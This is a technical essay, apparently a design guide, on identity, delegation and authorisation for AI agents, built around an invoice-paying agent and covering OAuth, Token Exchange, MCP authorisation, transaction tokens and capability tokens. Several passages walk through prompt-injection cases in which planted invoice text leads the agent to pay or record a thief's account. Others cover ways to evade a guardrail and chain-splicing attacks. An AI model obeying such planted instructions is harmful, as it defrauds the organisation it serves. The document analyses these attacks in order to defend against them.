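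*Governing Dynamic Capabilities* proposes replay when no TEE is available, which it describes as the norm for cloud models. An auditor runs the declared model again on the recorded inputs and compares the outputs. The auditor needs access to the declared model, and its outputs must be reproducible enough to compare. If Acme can only call the same provider again, replay may reveal that the model has changed since last week, but not that the provider was using a model other than the declared one all along.

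*AI Identity* (2026) distinguishes proof that certain code is running from proof that a certain model produced a certain output. *TensorCommitments* (2026) works towards the second kind of proof. The provider commits to the intermediate values that the model computes, and the customer checks the commitment without running the whole model again. This adds work equal to 0.97% of one pass through the model for the provider and 0.12% for the customer. A customer can't add the method without the provider's help, but the extra work is a weak reason for the provider to refuse.

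Until providers offer such proofs, Acme can request a fixed model version where one exists and run the same test invoices through it every day. These tests may detect a change in behaviour, though they don't identify the weights.

### Identical measurements, different payments

Suppose Acme runs two copies of the invoice agent with the same image, weights, prompt and tools. One reads a genuine invoice and pays €4,800 to the supplier's usual account. The other reads an invoice with a planted line about "new bank details" and pays €4,800 to a thief. Both copies produce the same measurements and pass the same checks, because the measured parts are the same.

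Novak and Birkholz (2026), in *Trustworthy Workload Identities WIMSE Profile for Replica Workloads*, define replicas as workloads whose functions clients cannot tell apart, and expect them to share code and security-sensitive configuration. This definition suits two copies of a payroll service, which should give the same answer to the same request. But two copies of an agent can share the same code and configuration and still respond differently to the same request, because they have already read different things.

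Acme could also hash the context. The hash would help an investigator prove later which text the model had read, but it wouldn't help a verifier decide whether to allow the payment. The verifier would need a reference value to compare it with, and none exists because nobody at Acme approved the invoice's wording before it arrived.

Another approach is to attest a check on what the agent reads and writes. Jin and colleagues run a guardrail, a filter for unsafe content, in a TEE and prove to users that it ran. They don't measure the agent, so its developer can keep it private. In their tests, the filter and the agent's responses took 25% to 38% longer than without a TEE. The machine cost 18.5 times as much, but at about 19 cents an hour, that is little compared with the €1.8 million an agent can pay out in that time.

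The filter's accuracy is a bigger concern. The content filter that Jin and colleagues tested caught only 54% of the unsafe examples, and a malicious developer can study its public code to find ways around it. The researchers warn against advertising their proof as proof of safety.

*Attestation is All You Need* (2026) presents AEGIS, a system that attests whether an agent's observed actions satisfy constraints derived from the job it was authorised to do. For the invoice agent, one constraint might be to pay only accounts in Acme's supplier records. The thief's payment would then fail the check even though the agent was running exactly the software Acme had approved. But AEGIS can check this only once the agent has started to act, so passing the check can't be a condition for issuing the agent's first credential.

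## Giving the agent a person's authority

The invoice agent can now prove its name and, if Acme uses attestation, which software it is running. Neither proof shows whose authority the agent is using when it pays an invoice. It might be working for Alice, Bob or the finance department, and that determines whose limit applies and who is responsible for a mistake.

### Acting as itself, for Alice or as Alice

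Suppose the agent pays a supplier €4,800. The way the agent obtained its access affects what an investigator later finds in the payment service's log.

| How the agent acts | What it presents | Log entry |
|---|---|---|
| As itself | a token that names only the agent | invoice agent paid €4,800 |
| For Alice (delegation) | a token that names both | invoice agent paid €4,800 for Alice |
| As Alice (impersonation) | her password, her session or a token that names only her | Alice paid €4,800 |

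OAuth calls each procedure for obtaining an access token a grant. An agent that acts as itself can use the client credentials grant, in which it authenticates to Acme's authorisation server, which issues the tokens, and no user takes part. Kasselman and colleagues want the agent to authenticate with its workload credential, not a static secret. The grant suits jobs that no particular person asked for, such as collecting new invoices from a shared mailbox overnight. It suits payments less well, because Acme would have to give the agent payment rights of its own and the log wouldn't show who wanted the supplier paid.

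*OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Jones, Nadalin and colleagues) describes how an authorisation server can deliberately allow impersonation without a shared password. For example, the server can issue the agent a token that names only Alice and works at one service for one minute. That is much safer than giving the agent her password, but the log still names only Alice. A paper for the OpenID Foundation, which publishes login standards built on OAuth, reports that services often log agents' calls this way and recommends delegation instead (South, 2025, *Identity Management for Agentic AI*). Delegation is the best choice for Alice's payments because the agent's name lets the payment service apply the €5,000 limit and Alice's name shows who authorised the work.

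### How Alice approves the agent

For delegation by a user, Kasselman and colleagues recommend OAuth's authorisation code grant.

1. The agent sends Alice's browser to the authorisation server. The request names the agent, the payment service and the permissions the agent wants. It also contains a hash of a random secret that the agent has just generated.
2. Alice logs in, preferably with a passkey or another method that resists phishing. The agent never handles her login details.
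3. The authorisation server shows her the permissions, and she approves them.
4. The server sends her browser back to the agent with a temporary code.
5. The agent contacts the server directly to exchange the code for an access token. It authenticates with its workload credential, for example over mutual TLS, and reveals the random secret. A thief who intercepted the code would have neither.
6. The server returns the access token.

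Steps 2 and 5 answer different questions. Alice's login shows that she is Alice, but someone else's program could be asking for her approval. The agent's credential shows which program is asking, but not that she agreed. If Acme has registered the agent under its SPIFFE name, the token from step 6 contains these fields:

| Field | Value | Meaning |
|---|---|---|
| `client_id` | `spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice` | the agent |
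| `sub` | `alice@acme.example` | the user it acts for |
| `aud` | `https://pay.acme.example` | the only service that should accept the token |
| `scope` | `payments:write` | what the agent may do there |
| `exp` | 09:05 | expiry, five minutes after issue |

An ordinary OAuth access token is a bearer token, so a thief could use this one until 09:05. The payment service can reduce the risk by comparing `client_id` with the name in the caller's certificate. FAPI, an OpenID Foundation security profile for services such as bank transfers, goes further by requiring tokens bound to the sender's key, as South explains.

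The agent needs 12 of these tokens to work for an hour. The authorisation server can also issue a refresh token, which the agent exchanges for new access tokens without asking Alice again. This is convenient for long tasks, but the agent may still be using her approval after she has gone home.

### Exchanging Alice's token for one that names the agent

Suppose Alice instead starts from Acme's finance portal, which already holds a token for her, and asks the agent to pay this week's invoices. Jones and colleagues' Token Exchange, published as RFC 8693, lets the agent turn her token into one for the payment service without another trip through her browser. The agent sends the authorisation server:

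- a **subject token**, which represents Alice, the person on whose behalf the agent is asking
- an **actor token**, which represents the agent
- the service where it wants to use the new token, and the scopes it needs there.

The server validates both tokens. Alice's token may also contain a `may_act` field, which names a party that is allowed to act for her. If it names the invoice agent and the canteen's menu program presents the token, the server can refuse the exchange. If the exchange succeeds, the agent could receive this:

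```json
{
  "iss": "https://auth.acme.example",
  "aud": "https://pay.acme.example",
  "exp": 1796634300,
  "scope": "payments:write",
  "sub": "alice@acme.example",
  "act": {
    "sub": "spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice"
  }
}
```

The outer `sub` is Alice, and the `act` field (short for "actor") identifies the agent acting for her. Because `act` can only identify, an expiry time inside it would have no meaning, so the token can't give the agent an earlier expiry than its own. An `act` field can contain another `act` field, so a token can record a chain of actors.

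Without an actor token, this procedure can't produce delegation, so the server can only return a token that names only Alice. Even with an actor token, the server's policy determines whether it adds `act`. To find out whether Acme uses delegation, an auditor should therefore decode a token the server issued, because the agent's request doesn't show whether the server added `act`.

The standard lets a server accept exchanges without authenticating the program that asks, which could let a thief trade Alice's stolen token for others. If the agent lists `read` and `write` in one request that names both the mail server and the payment service, it is asking for both permissions at both services, although it may only need to read mail. Requesting access to one service at a time avoids this.

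The agent's name can also end up in different fields. In the authorisation code grant, it is in `client_id`. If the portal carries out an exchange for the agent, `client_id` names the portal and `act` names the agent. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) points out that existing specifications don't represent delegated actors consistently across token types, and proposes common rules. Until services adopt these or similar rules, Acme has to decide where its payment service looks for the agent's name, and should reject tokens that don't have it there.

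### Stating the €5,000 limit

The scope `payments:write` permits payments of any size to anyone. Acme could keep the €5,000 limit in the payment service's own rules, but then Alice wouldn't see it when she approves the agent, and she couldn't choose a lower limit for a smaller job. Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell, in *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, published as RFC 9396, add a field called `authorization_details` for permissions like this:

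```json
"authorization_details": [
  {
    "type": "https://acme.example/invoice-payment",
    "actions": ["initiate"],
    "locations": ["https://pay.acme.example"],
    "maxAmountPerPayment": {
      "currency": "EUR",
      "amount": "5000.00"
    }
  }
]
```

The agent includes the limit in its request. The authorisation server shows it to Alice, records what she approves and makes that available to the payment service, usually by copying it into the access token. The payment service then has to enforce it.

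The standard defines `type`, `actions` and `locations`, while Acme added `maxAmountPerPayment` itself. Whoever designs an interface decides which fields each type allows, and the authorisation server must refuse a request with an unknown type or field. If a developer misspells the limit's name, the request therefore fails, whereas a server that ignored unknown fields would issue a token with no limit.

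An object permits every combination of the actions and data types it lists. If it lists the actions "read" and "write" and the data types "invoices" and "payments", the agent can read and write both invoices and payments. To let the agent read invoices and write payments, and nothing else, Acme needs two objects.

This flexibility also makes requests harder to compare. If the agent later asks for a token with a €2,000 limit, the authorisation server has to work out that this is less than Alice approved. Lodderstedt and colleagues acknowledge that no standard method can compare two arbitrary requests, because fields mean different things in different interfaces. Acme therefore has to write the comparison for its own payment type. Zehavi (2026) adds in *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling* that clients have no standard way to discover what a type should contain, so the parties have to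 agree on it beforehand. Zehavi proposes a format that clients could look up. For now, the method is easier to use between Acme's own systems than with a supplier whose payment interface the agent has never encountered.

The limit still applies to each payment separately, so it doesn't cap the total. Acme could add a field for a daily limit, but the token doesn't change as the agent spends, so the payment service would have to keep a running total and carry it over when the agent gets a new token.

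Some conditions are harder to enforce, because a field can limit the agent only if some component has the information to check it. Alice wants the agent to pay only genuine invoices. Acme could define a field called `genuineInvoicesOnly` and set it to true, and the authorisation server would accept it. But the payment service receives an amount, an account number and a reference, and can't determine from these whether the invoice was real.

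Acme can replace parts of the condition with things it can check, such as whether the account is in its supplier records and whether the invoice number matches an order. These checks would stop a payment to the planted "new bank details", but not payment of an invoice from a real supplier for goods that never arrived.

Alternatively, the agent could ask Alice to approve each payment separately. In Lodderstedt and colleagues' example, the request specifies an exact amount, a named recipient and an account number. But if the agent copies those details from a forged invoice, Alice's approval page will show the thief's account number beside the supplier's name. If she approves it, the token will record her consent to the wrong payment.

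### OAuth in the Model Context Protocol

Acme may also offer the payment service to agents through a Model Context Protocol (MCP) server, a program that provides tools that agents can call. The current version of the protocol dates from 28 July 2026. In November, Delimarsky and Soria Parra were still organising the next release and announced plans for two a year (*A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP*, 2026).

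Under the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), the MCP server accepts access tokens and the agent's MCP client requests them. When the client first calls without a token, the server refuses and returns the address of a document that identifies its authorisation server. The client sends Alice's browser to the authorisation server and continues with the authorisation code grant. The client must name the MCP server in a `resource` parameter, and the MCP server must reject any token that wasn't issued for it.

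According to Tabata's *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (2026), the July version of MCP made six changes to authorisation. None introduces a new idea, and the basic OAuth procedure was already there. One requires the client to check which authorisation server a response came from, whenever the response includes that information. Without this check, an attacker who runs one authorisation server could trick the client into sending it a code issued by another server.

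For Acme, some details of the protocol matter more than the overall procedure:

- Authorisation is optional. A server that runs on the agent's own machine and communicates through standard input and output takes its credentials from its environment instead. "Supports MCP" therefore doesn't mean "checks tokens".
- The client sends the access token as a bearer token, so Acme needs a separate check, such as mutual TLS, to establish that the invoice agent sent it.
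- A client can use a web address as its `client_id` and publish a description of itself there. If Acme does this, it needs a record that links the address to the agent's SPIFFE name.

That last method replaces one in which clients registered themselves automatically. South criticised automatic registration because a public registration page lets anyone create a client with no link to an accountable person or company. The July version keeps it only for compatibility. Older servers may still depend on it, and Dhamsania (2026) warns in *MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times* that these servers may not have kept up with the changes. Acme should ask which version a server implements before giving it access to payments.

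If the MCP server has to call the bank to send the money, the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) require it to use a separate token from the bank's authorisation server. They forbid forwarding the token that the server received from the agent, although that would be the easiest approach to code.

The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* (2025) gives the reasons. The MCP server may limit how often an agent pays or check each request for errors. If the agent's token also worked at the bank, the agent or a thief could call the bank directly and avoid those checks. The MCP server also couldn't tell its clients apart if they used tokens issued by the bank, which would damage the audit trail. Kasselman and colleagues add that forwarding tokens makes theft more likely and lets an attacker move from one service to the next.

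The rule leaves open how the MCP server gets its token for the bank. In October 2025, South found that this often depended on custom code. Where the same authorisation server covers both services, Kasselman and colleagues suggest Token Exchange, which can produce a new token that names both Alice and the agent. The MCP server also follows the rule if it uses its own account at the bank, but then the bank's log names neither Alice nor the agent. Acme would need to record a shared transaction number in both systems to connect the payment to Alice. More may change soon, because *The New MCP Roadmap* (Soria Parra and Delimarsky, 2026) lists agent identity among its priorities.

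### Too much authority, or the wrong person's

All these mechanisms rely on Alice approving roughly what the task needs. Asking her about each payment could mean 360 requests an hour, or one every 10 seconds, and nobody could review them properly at that rate. South describes a similar case, in which an agent makes hundreds of calls in seconds to reallocate an advertising budget, and predicts that users will start to approve requests without reading them. The alternative, a broad approval at the start, gives the agent permissions it may never need. South's cases are hypothetical, and the paper doesn't measure how often people over-approve.

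MCP's rules for choosing scopes can make this worse. If the server's refusal doesn't state which scopes a request needs, the client asks for every scope on the server's published list. That list is supposed to be minimal, but the server's operator writes it. When a later call needs another scope, the protocol recommends that the client request the earlier scopes again along with the new one, so that it doesn't lose permissions it still needs. An agent that corrected one supplier's address on Monday may therefore still have permission to change supplier records on Friday.

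South proposes setting limits in advance, such as a budget and a list of approved recipients, and having the service enforce them. Alice, for example, could give one approval for this week's invoices that caps each payment and the total, and allows payments only to existing suppliers. She would then read one page carefully instead of skimming 360. Acme should also start a new grant for each job, so that permissions from the last one don't carry over.

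An agent also inherits all of Alice's permissions when it works through her browser while she is logged in. South points out that such agents bypass the controls on programming interfaces, and that services can hardly distinguish their actions from the user's. If Alice can edit supplier records, so can the agent. An instruction planted in an invoice could then lead it to replace a supplier's account number in the records before paying, so the payment would pass the check against those records.

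Delegation avoids this only if the payment service combines the two parties' rights correctly. The agent should be able to do only what all three of these allow:

effective rights = Alice's rights ∩ the agent's rights ∩ the token's permissions

If Alice's limit is €10,000 and the agent's is €5,000, the agent can pay up to €5,000 on her behalf. The OAuth standards supply the identifiers but not this rule. Kasselman and colleagues require services to use both identifiers, and Acme has to write the policy that combines them. A service that reads only `sub` will apply Alice's limit. To test for this, Acme can have the agent request a €7,000 payment, which Alice could make herself. If the payment goes through, the service is ignoring the agent's identifier.

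The formula and the `sub` field each allow for only one user. South describes a chief financial officer whose agent answers questions in a group chat. The officer may see salaries but some people in the chat may not, and the agent can reveal them even though its token is valid. Similarly, if Alice asks Acme's agent in a group chat why a payment failed, it could post a supplier's bank details to colleagues who have no access to them.

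One solution is to let the agent read only what every member of the chat may read. South notes that no standard method exists for this, and that detailed access rules can help but are complex to set up. This restriction would also make the agent less useful to Alice whenever someone with fewer rights joined. Acme could instead run the agent separately for each person and reply to them privately. Each run needs its own context as well as its own token, because otherwise whatever the agent read with Alice's token would still be in its context when Bob asks the next question.

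## Passing authority to sub-agents and other organisations

Suppose an invoice from Brandt Tools, one of Acme's suppliers, gives a new account number, and Acme's rules require someone to check it before the invoice agent pays €4,800. Acme buys these checks from an outside firm, Checkwell, whose agent compares account numbers with bank records. Alice has delegated to the invoice agent, which now has to delegate this check to a program that Acme didn't write and doesn't run.

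### Authority may only shrink

The basic rule is that nobody can pass on more authority than they hold. Reece (2026), in *Cross-Organizational Delegation for Workload and Agent Identity*, a problem statement addressed to the WIMSE group, calls this narrowing attenuation. If *A*₀ is the set of actions open to Alice, *A*₁ the set open to the first agent acting for her, and so on, then:

*A*₀ ⊇ *A*₁ ⊇ *A*₂ ⊇ … ⊇ *A*ₙ

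| | Payments | Supplier records |
|---|---|---|
| Alice (*A*₀) | up to €10,000 per invoice | read and edit all |
| Invoice agent, for Alice (*A*₁) | up to €5,000 per payment | read all |
| Checking agent, for Alice (*A*₂) | none | read the Brandt Tools record |

If the checking agent asks to pay €1, Acme has to refuse, although Alice and the invoice agent could each make that payment. The invoice agent also can't let the checking agent correct the Brandt Tools record, because only Alice, and not the invoice agent, may edit it.

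A server can guarantee the rule by calculating each new set as an intersection:

*A*ₙ₊₁ = *A*ₙ ∩ (what the next agent may ever do) ∩ (what this grant allows)

An intersection is contained in each of the sets that form it, so *A*ₙ₊₁ always fits inside *A*ₙ. The two can be equal, which means an agent that passes all of its authority to a sub-agent is still following the rule. Someone therefore still has to decide how much authority the sub-agent needs.

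The rule doesn't limit totals either. If the invoice agent starts five payment sub-agents and gives each the €5,000 limit, every grant is within the invoice agent's own authority. But working at the same pace as the invoice agent, the five could pay out €9 million an hour, compared with €1.8 million for the invoice agent alone. To prevent this, Acme has to divide the invoice agent's budget among the sub-agents or have the payment service enforce a limit on their combined total.

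### Nested actors in Token Exchange

If Acme's authorisation server lets the checking agent read supplier records for Alice, nested `act` fields in the token could record the chain of actors like this:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://auth.acme.example",
  "aud": "https://suppliers.acme.example",
  "exp": 1796634300,
  "scope": "suppliers:read",
  "sub": "alice@acme.example",
  "act": {
    "sub": "spiffe://checkwell.example/agents/bank-check",
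    "act": {
      "sub": "spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice"
    }
  }
}
```

The outer `act` names the current actor, Checkwell's agent, and the `act` nested inside it names the previous actor, the invoice agent. With more hops, the earliest actor would be the most deeply nested.

RFC 8693 requires a service to base access decisions only on the token's top-level fields and the current actor. Earlier actors are "informational only". If Acme suspended the invoice agent a minute ago, a supplier-record service that follows the RFC still can't refuse this token just because it lists the invoice agent as an earlier actor.

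The inner fields would also be a weak basis for a decision. They identify the earlier actors but don't record what each was allowed to do, and the RFC doesn't require those actors to sign anything. The service therefore has to trust the issuing server about who took part, and can't check whether authority shrank as it passed from one actor to the next.

The whole chain has to be enforced when the server issues each token. In the exchange that produced this token, the server received one that still listed the invoice agent as the current actor, so it could have refused because of the suspension. It could also have compared the requested permissions with those in the old token. If every server makes that comparison at every hop, authority shrinks along the whole chain. The server should write the result into top-level fields, such as `scope` or `authorization_details`, because services may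 rely on those. Here it should also restrict access to one supplier, since `suppliers:read` alone covers them all.

This works within Acme, where one company controls the server, but an outside recipient has no proof that each server made the comparison. Reece counts this among the main gaps in Token Exchange. Later changes to the first token also may not affect the others. Jones and colleagues describe an exchange as a one-time event that doesn't tightly link the old and new tokens, so revoking Alice's token doesn't necessarily invalidate the checking agent's.

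### Transaction tokens within one organisation

Even a single payment at Acme may pass through a gateway that receives the request, a service that checks limits, a ledger, and a connector to the bank. If these programs forward the agent's access token to one another, an attacker who finds it in any of their logs can start a different payment. *Transaction Tokens* (Tulshibagwale, Fletcher and Kasselman, 2026) proposes replacing the access token with a token limited to that transaction.

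1. The invoice agent sends the gateway its access token and a request to pay Brandt Tools €4,800.
2. The gateway authenticates to Acme's transaction token service. It sends the access token, the purpose of the transaction and the payment details.
3. The service validates the access token, applies its own policy and returns a signed transaction token.
4. The gateway calls the limit checker with this token in an HTTP header named `Txn-Token`.
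5. The limit checker verifies the signature, trust domain and expiry time, then passes the token unchanged to the ledger, which does the same before calling the bank connector.

The token for this payment could contain:

| Field | Value | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| `aud` | `acme.example` | the only trust domain that may accept it |
| `txn` | `txn-90417` | unique number of the transaction |
| `sub` | `alice@acme.example` | the party for whom the transaction runs |
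| `req_wl` | `spiffe://acme.example/gateway` | the workload that requested the token |
| `scope` | `invoice.pay` | the purpose, as narrow as possible |
| `tctx` | €4,800, the account number, the invoice number | details that must stay the same |
| `rctx` | the caller's network address | circumstances of the request |
| `exp` | 09:02 | expiry, two minutes after issue |

Transaction tokens are expected to last minutes or less, and the draft's example lasts six minutes. A compromised ledger can't change €4,800 to €48,000 in the token without breaking the signature. But this protects the payment only if the bank connector takes the amount from the token or compares the token with the request it receives, and the draft leaves that logic to each company. The signature also doesn't make the original details correct. If the agent copied a thief's account number from a forged invoice, the token will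 carry that number unchanged to the bank.

The token service must keep the new token's scope within that of the original token, and must reject a request if it can't determine the original scope. A program further down the chain may request a replacement token with fewer permissions, but the replacement can't add permissions or change the user, trust domain or transaction number. A replacement can last longer than the token it replaces, so Tulshibagwale and colleagues recommend limiting the number of replacements.

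A thief can replay a stolen transaction token until it expires, unless all copies of the receiving service share a record of the transaction numbers they have already accepted. The token also doesn't authenticate the program that sends it, so Acme still needs mutual TLS or signed requests between its services.

The invoice agent is missing from the table. `sub` identifies Alice and `req_wl` identifies the gateway, so the token doesn't show that an agent made the request unless Acme adds the agent's name to the context. *Transaction Tokens For Agents* (Raut, 2026) proposes an `actor` field for the agent and a `principal` field for whoever started its work. That was an individual draft, due to expire in October 2026. The main draft, by Tulshibagwale and colleagues, is much further along. It had working group consensus by August, and the group planned to submit it for approval in December.

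### Crossing into another organisation's domain

Acme's transaction token is valid only in Acme's domain, so Checkwell can't accept it. Checkwell has its own authorisation server, which issues the access tokens that its checking agent accepts. *OAuth Identity and Authorization Chaining Across Domains* (Schwenkschuster, Kasselman and colleagues, 2026) connects the two organisations' servers through a signed document called a JWT authorisation grant. Acme's agent gets the grant from Acme's server and exchanges it at Checkwell's server for an access token.

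1. The invoice agent sends Acme's authorisation server the access token or transaction token it holds, and asks for a grant addressed to Checkwell's authorisation server. This is a Token Exchange.
2. Acme's server validates the token, applies Acme's policy and returns a signed grant that identifies Alice.
3. The agent presents the grant to Checkwell's authorisation server.
4. Checkwell's server checks the signature against a key it already trusts as Acme's. It applies its own policy and returns an access token for the checking agent.
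5. The invoice agent calls the checking agent with this token and asks it to check the Brandt Tools account.

Acme's original token never leaves Acme. If Checkwell's agent then needs to call a bank that uses a third authorisation server, it repeats the procedure, since the IETF's June 2026 draft uses the same protocol at every boundary. By August 2026 the draft was with the RFC Editor, the last stage before publication as a standard. The IETF's approval notice reports many implementations, including version 26.5 of Keycloak, an open-source identity server.

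Chaining preserves information about Alice, but it doesn't prove that authority shrank. Acme's permission might be called `suppliers:read` and Checkwell's `account-check:run`. No general rule can determine whether one contains the other, so the two companies have to agree on a mapping. They also have to agree on where in the grant to identify the invoice agent. McGuinness's proposed rules for `act` would settle this for grants, as well as for access and transaction tokens.

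Acme could avoid some of this by giving Checkwell less access. If the invoice agent includes the supplier's name and account number in its request, the checking agent doesn't need to read Acme's supplier records.

A second method is simpler when both companies already use the same identity provider, a service through which employees sign in once and then use many applications. *Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant* (Parecki, McGuinness and Campbell, 2026) lets an application use that sign-in to get access elsewhere.

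1. Alice signs in through Acme's identity provider. The application that runs the invoice agent receives an identity assertion, a signed statement of who she is.
2. The application sends the assertion to the identity provider and asks for a grant addressed to Checkwell's authorisation server.
3. The identity provider checks whether Acme's policy permits this connection and returns the grant.
4. The application presents the grant to Checkwell's server, which already trusts Acme's identity provider for sign-on.
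5. Checkwell's server returns an access token, and the agent makes its call.

The main difference is that this method starts from a statement that Alice signed in, rather than from a token that already carries some of her authority. Kasselman and colleagues consider it best suited to companies that connect many online services through one identity provider, because Alice doesn't have to log in again at each service. When there is no such statement, they recommend the general method.

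Central control can also replace repeated approval pages. An extension to the Model Context Protocol that became stable in June 2026 lets companies arrange access to MCP servers through their identity provider, so the servers are already connected when employees first log in. The announcement, *Enterprise-Managed Authorization* (Carleton, 2026), lists repeated consent prompts among users' biggest complaints. The administrator's choice then matters more, because Alice may never see a page where she could choose a lower limit.

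Both methods assume that Checkwell already knows which keys belong to Acme. Reece argues that this won't be practical when agents from many organisations meet without prior arrangement. Public infrastructure could let Checkwell look up an unknown company's keys, but someone still has to establish that those keys belong to the real company. Reece proposes checking this carefully once, at first contact, and then having later keys signed by earlier ones.

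### The Workload Authorization Grant

Checkwell may have more than one checking agent. If it uses a hosted agent platform, its staff might create a new agent for every client or job, and registering each one at Acme would be slow. The Workload Authorization Grant, the draft mentioned earlier for platforms with many agents, addresses this case. Its November 2026 version has five authors, from Anthropic, OpenAI, Okta, Defakto Security and Ping Identity.

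Suppose Checkwell's agents do need to read account numbers in Acme's supplier records. Under the more detailed August version, it would work like this:

1. An Acme administrator records once, at Acme's authorisation server, that it should trust the issuer the platform operates for Checkwell. The administrator also sets a rule, such as "agents with the role `bank-checker` may read account numbers".
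2. A Checkwell employee creates an agent on the platform. Nobody has to inform Acme.
3. The platform signs a grant that contains the agent's permanent identifier, the intended recipient, an expiry time, and properties such as the agent's groups and roles.
4. The agent presents the grant to Acme's authorisation server and names the service it wants to use.
5. The server finds the issuer's public key and checks the grant. It must not reject the agent merely because it has never encountered it. It then applies Acme's rules and, if they permit access, returns an access token.

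Carleton's sample grant is valid for five minutes. The server may not issue refresh tokens, so an agent that works for an hour needs new grants from the platform. When Checkwell retires an agent, the platform stops signing grants for it, and its access ends once its remaining grants and access tokens expire. With five-minute grants and five-minute access tokens, that takes at most about ten minutes.

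Acme decides what a `bank-checker` may do, but Checkwell and its platform decide which agents get that role. If a Checkwell employee carelessly gives it to a marketing agent, that agent gains access to Acme's account numbers. Acme should therefore attach modest permissions to each property and ask Checkwell who can assign those properties. The draft also requires the platform to use a separate issuer for each customer. Otherwise Acme's server would have to use other fields in the grant to distinguish Checkwell's agents from another customer's, and a mistake could give the wrong company's agents access.

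The grant is a bearer document, and the draft lists proof of possession as an open issue. The grant covers only agents that act on their own behalf, so it doesn't make the checking agent part of Alice's chain. When the grant is used alone, the checking agent's authority comes from Acme's policy, not from Alice, so her limits don't constrain the agent and her name doesn't appear in the log. Carleton and colleagues intend the grant to be combined with delegation methods in which the agent is the actor.

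By its own description, the draft is early and exploratory and "does not describe a shipped or committed design". Companies have nevertheless started to use it. Pogorelec (2026), in *Anthropic tests giving Claude agents their own credentials*, reports that Anthropic announced beta support in two products in December. The monitoring company Datadog and the analytics company PostHog accept the grants in their MCP servers, and CVS Health uses them to connect agents to its internal MCP servers. Acme could reasonably try it for reading low-risk data, but should expect the details to change.

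### Tokens that a holder can narrow offline

With all the OAuth methods above, the invoice agent has to contact a server to get a narrower token. A capability token itself carries the authority, and its holder can add restrictions without asking anyone. Macaroons, which Google researchers introduced in 2014, do this with HMAC, a function that computes a fingerprint from a key and a text. Anyone with the key can repeat the calculation, but nobody can feasibly work back from the fingerprint to the key.

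Suppose Acme's supplier-record service holds a secret key *k* and issues the invoice agent a macaroon for reading records. The agent then narrows it for Checkwell:

*t*₀ = HMAC(*k*, "token 58")
*t*₁ = HMAC(*t*₀, "read only")
*t*₂ = HMAC(*t*₁, "only Brandt Tools")
*t*₃ = HMAC(*t*₂, "until 09:10")

The agent receives the first two texts and *t*₁. It adds two conditions, computes *t*₃, and sends Checkwell all four texts but only *t*₃. Checkwell's agent can add a fourth condition in the same way, but it can't remove "until 09:10" without *t*₂, which it doesn't have. The service starts from *k*, repeats the calculation and compares the result with the one it received. It then checks that the request meets every condition.

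Every service that checks a macaroon needs the secret key, which would also let it create new ones. Biscuit and UCAN (User Controlled Authorization Network) avoid this problem by using public-key signatures.

| | How the holder narrows it | Who can check it | Does it name each holder? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Macaroon | adds a condition and computes a new fingerprint | whoever has the secret key | no |
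| Biscuit | adds a block of rules, signed with a one-time key | anyone with the issuer's public key | not by default |
| UCAN | signs a new delegation to the next holder's public key | anyone who can identify the resource owner's key | yes |

A Biscuit's rules are written in a small logic language. A UCAN chain consists of separate signed delegations, and the recipient checks that each one grants no more authority than the one before. UCAN is the closest match to the chain of subsets, because an outside firm can do this check itself. Only the holder of the named key can use a UCAN, whereas macaroons and Biscuits are bearer tokens unless someone adds a condition that ties them to a key.

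Offline narrowing makes revocation harder because the issuer doesn't know which narrower tokens exist. The simplest remedy is to cancel the original token and everything derived from it. Biscuits give each block its own identifier, and UCAN lets a delegator cancel one branch, but every service that accepts the tokens needs an up-to-date list of cancellations. Reece calls the conflict between offline checking and timely revocation a central tension, and wants recipients to refuse requests when their list is too old. If Acme used such a token for payments and the service updated its list every ten minutes, an agent could make another 60 payments, worth up to €300,000, after its token was cancelled.

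Capability tokens are also harder to adopt. MCP and AIMS use OAuth, so a typical MCP server can't read a capability token. The sender and the receiving service also have to agree on what each condition means, and the service must refuse a token that contains a condition it doesn't understand. For Acme, these tokens make most sense between its own services, where agents create sub-agents so quickly that calls to an authorisation server become a burden. With Checkwell, OAuth chaining is more practical because it needs fewer changes on both sides.

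### Attacks on delegation chains

One weakness of Token Exchange is that it can combine two valid tokens from different tasks. Suppose Checkwell's agent works for Alice in the morning and for Bob in the afternoon. An attacker who has compromised the agent could present Bob's token as the subject token, along with an actor token from Alice's job. RFC 8693 requires the server to validate each token, but not to check that both come from the same task. The server could then sign a token recording a delegation that never took place, which is called chain splicing. The `may_act` field helps only partly, because Bob's token may correctly name the agent as allowed to act for him.

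Acme's server could put the same transaction number in all tokens for one task and refuse any pair of tokens whose numbers don't match. Recipients outside Acme need evidence they can check for themselves. *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) defines six ways to preserve a chain of actors across token exchanges, and distinguishes chains that a party declares from those that recipients can verify. Some of these disclose only part of the chain, which would let Acme hide its internal agents from Checkwell's subcontractors. The paper is an individual draft from June 2026, so Acme can't expect other companies to support it yet.

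Another attack makes an agent use its authority for the wrong person. Checkwell's agent is allowed to read all its clients' files. If someone at Acme asks it about an account in another client's file, and Checkwell checks only whether its agent can read files, Acme will receive the other client's data. Security engineers call this a confused deputy. Reece's remedy is to check, for every request, both whether the agent is allowed to perform this kind of action and whether the person it acts for is allowed to use this particular file.

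A safeguard can also disappear as authority passes along a chain. Suppose Acme requires a person to approve any payment above €3,000, but the token that the invoice agent obtains for a payment sub-agent omits this requirement. The sub-agent could then make the €4,800 payment without approval. Reece wants the requirement to be part of the delegated authority, so that later holders can tighten it but not remove it. The approval must cover the exact amount and account and work only once. A service that doesn't recognise the requirement must refuse the payment.

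None of these fixes helps if the sub-agent can get access another way. If Alice's password is stored on the machine where the sub-agent runs, it can log in as her and bypass the chain. Acme therefore has to remove such credentials from the agent's environment, and the payment service has to reject agents that use a person's login.

An attack may succeed without any agent exceeding its authority. The checking agent can't make payments, but its answer enters the invoice agent's context. If an attacker gets it to reply "account confirmed" about a thief's account, the invoice agent may pay €4,800 into that account with a valid token and within its limit, even though each step in the chain passed on less authority than the one before.

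## What identity checks leave undecided, and why behaviour is decided separately

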